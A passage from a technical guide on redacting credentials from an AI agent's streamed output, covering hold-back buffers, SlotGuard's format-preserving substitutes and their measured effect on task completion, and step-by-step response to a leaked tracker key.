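Holding back 12 characters is enough because the text so far can end with at most 12 characters of an incomplete key. If the filter held back only 11, a chunk that ended one character before the end of the key would cause it to release the key's first character, `t`. The filter would then never have the whole key at once, so it would release the rest too.

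In general, the filter must hold back one character fewer than the length of the longest key or encoded key it searches for. For a 40-character key, this delays the text by 39 characters, which users will hardly notice. An exact search can reduce the delay by holding text back only when it ends with the beginning of a key.

Some credentials have no fixed length. A private key in the common PEM format can run to thousands of characters, but it has clear opening and closing lines, so the filter can stop sending text at the first and resume after the second. Classifiers are harder to use with streams because the text that identifies a credential may come after it. Grafana doesn't support scanning a stream chunk by chunk, and its check on replies runs only once the full text is available.

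Holding text back doesn't help if the parts of a key arrive in separate messages or tool results. In a test by Xia and Park, all 200 keys split this way leaked when the filter used ordinary labels. SlotGuard stopped these leaks by keeping a record of related values throughout the session. The test used invented transcripts and did not include a capable attacker trying to reconstruct the values.

### What redaction breaks

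An agent may need the value that the filter removes. If the release agent reads a settings file with `[REDACTED]` in place of the database password and then saves the file, it overwrites the real password with the label. If the filter mistakes a commit hash for a key and removes it, the agent can't report which version of the product failed its tests.

Replacing each credential with a consistent label preserves some of the meaning. If the filter writes `[CREDENTIAL_1]` wherever one password appears and `[CREDENTIAL_2]` for another, the model can tell that two files use the same password and can then work out why a third file fails to connect. But if the model saves a file containing these labels, they replace the real credentials unless a trusted program can restore them. Grafana's second filter, for example, stores no record of what it removed, so the original values can't be restored from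 its output.

Replacing a credential with a label can also break the format of the surrounding text. For example, a program may reject a database address that has square brackets where the password should be. A model may also treat the credential as missing and request it. SlotGuard therefore replaces each credential with a fake one in the same format, and restores the real value on the user's machine when a local tool needs it. It also hides the private parts of file paths but keeps details such as the `.pdf` extension.

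Xia and Park compared these methods on 200 tasks with four models:

| What the model received | Tasks completed, lowest to highest |
|---|---|
| The original text | 93.5% to 100% |
| One general label for everything | 2.5% |
| Labels that gave the type of data | 20.5% to 38.5% |
| SlotGuard's substitutes | 89.5% to 100% |

The tasks involved file paths as well as credentials, and an agent can't open a file when a label has replaced its path. A filter that removed only credentials would therefore impair an agent less than these results suggest. In a separate test of 12 tasks, SlotGuard completed 83% with the fake credentials but only 50% without them, which suggests that their format matters.

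As with placeholders, a program that restores a real value in the wrong place can publish it, so the program has to check where each value is going. Xia and Park say that SlotGuard can't prevent theft by prompt injection.

### What to do after a leak

Suppose an engineer finds the tracker key in a public issue. Deleting the issue isn't enough, because someone may already have copied it. Chen and colleagues found that credentials which developers had removed from 107 original projects still existed in more than 50 forks, which are separate copies that other people control. The company should do the following:

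1. Revoke the key at the tracker. This makes every copy useless, including those the company will never find.
2. Create a new key and give it to the programs that need it. If `post_issue` can't be out of service even briefly, do this first and revoke the old key immediately afterwards.
3. Find out how the key got into the text and fix the cause. If the tests still inherit the environment variable, the next failed test could leak the new key too.
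4. Check the tracker's logs for everything anyone did with the old key since the earliest time it could have leaked. Look for unfamiliar IP addresses, new accounts and additional keys, since a thief may have created another way in.
5. Search for copies in transcripts, the agent's memory, application logs, issues, old commits and backups. Include the three Base64 forms.

The last search matters even after the key has stopped working, because the copies show who could have read the key and when, and other credentials may have leaked alongside it. The engineer should use an ordinary search program for this search, because asking the agent to find the key would put it back into the agent's context.

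The damage the thief could have done depends mostly on decisions the company made before the leak. A permanent key for the whole tracker works until someone notices the leak, which may take months, and the company then has to check every project. Suppose instead that at 10:40 the release agent leaks an access token that expires at 11:00 and can only create issues in `release`. The thief has 20 minutes to post false reports in one project. If the company discovers the leak the next morning, the token has already expired, and the engineer only has to check 20 minutes of logs for one project. If the refresh token leaked too, the company still has to revoke it.
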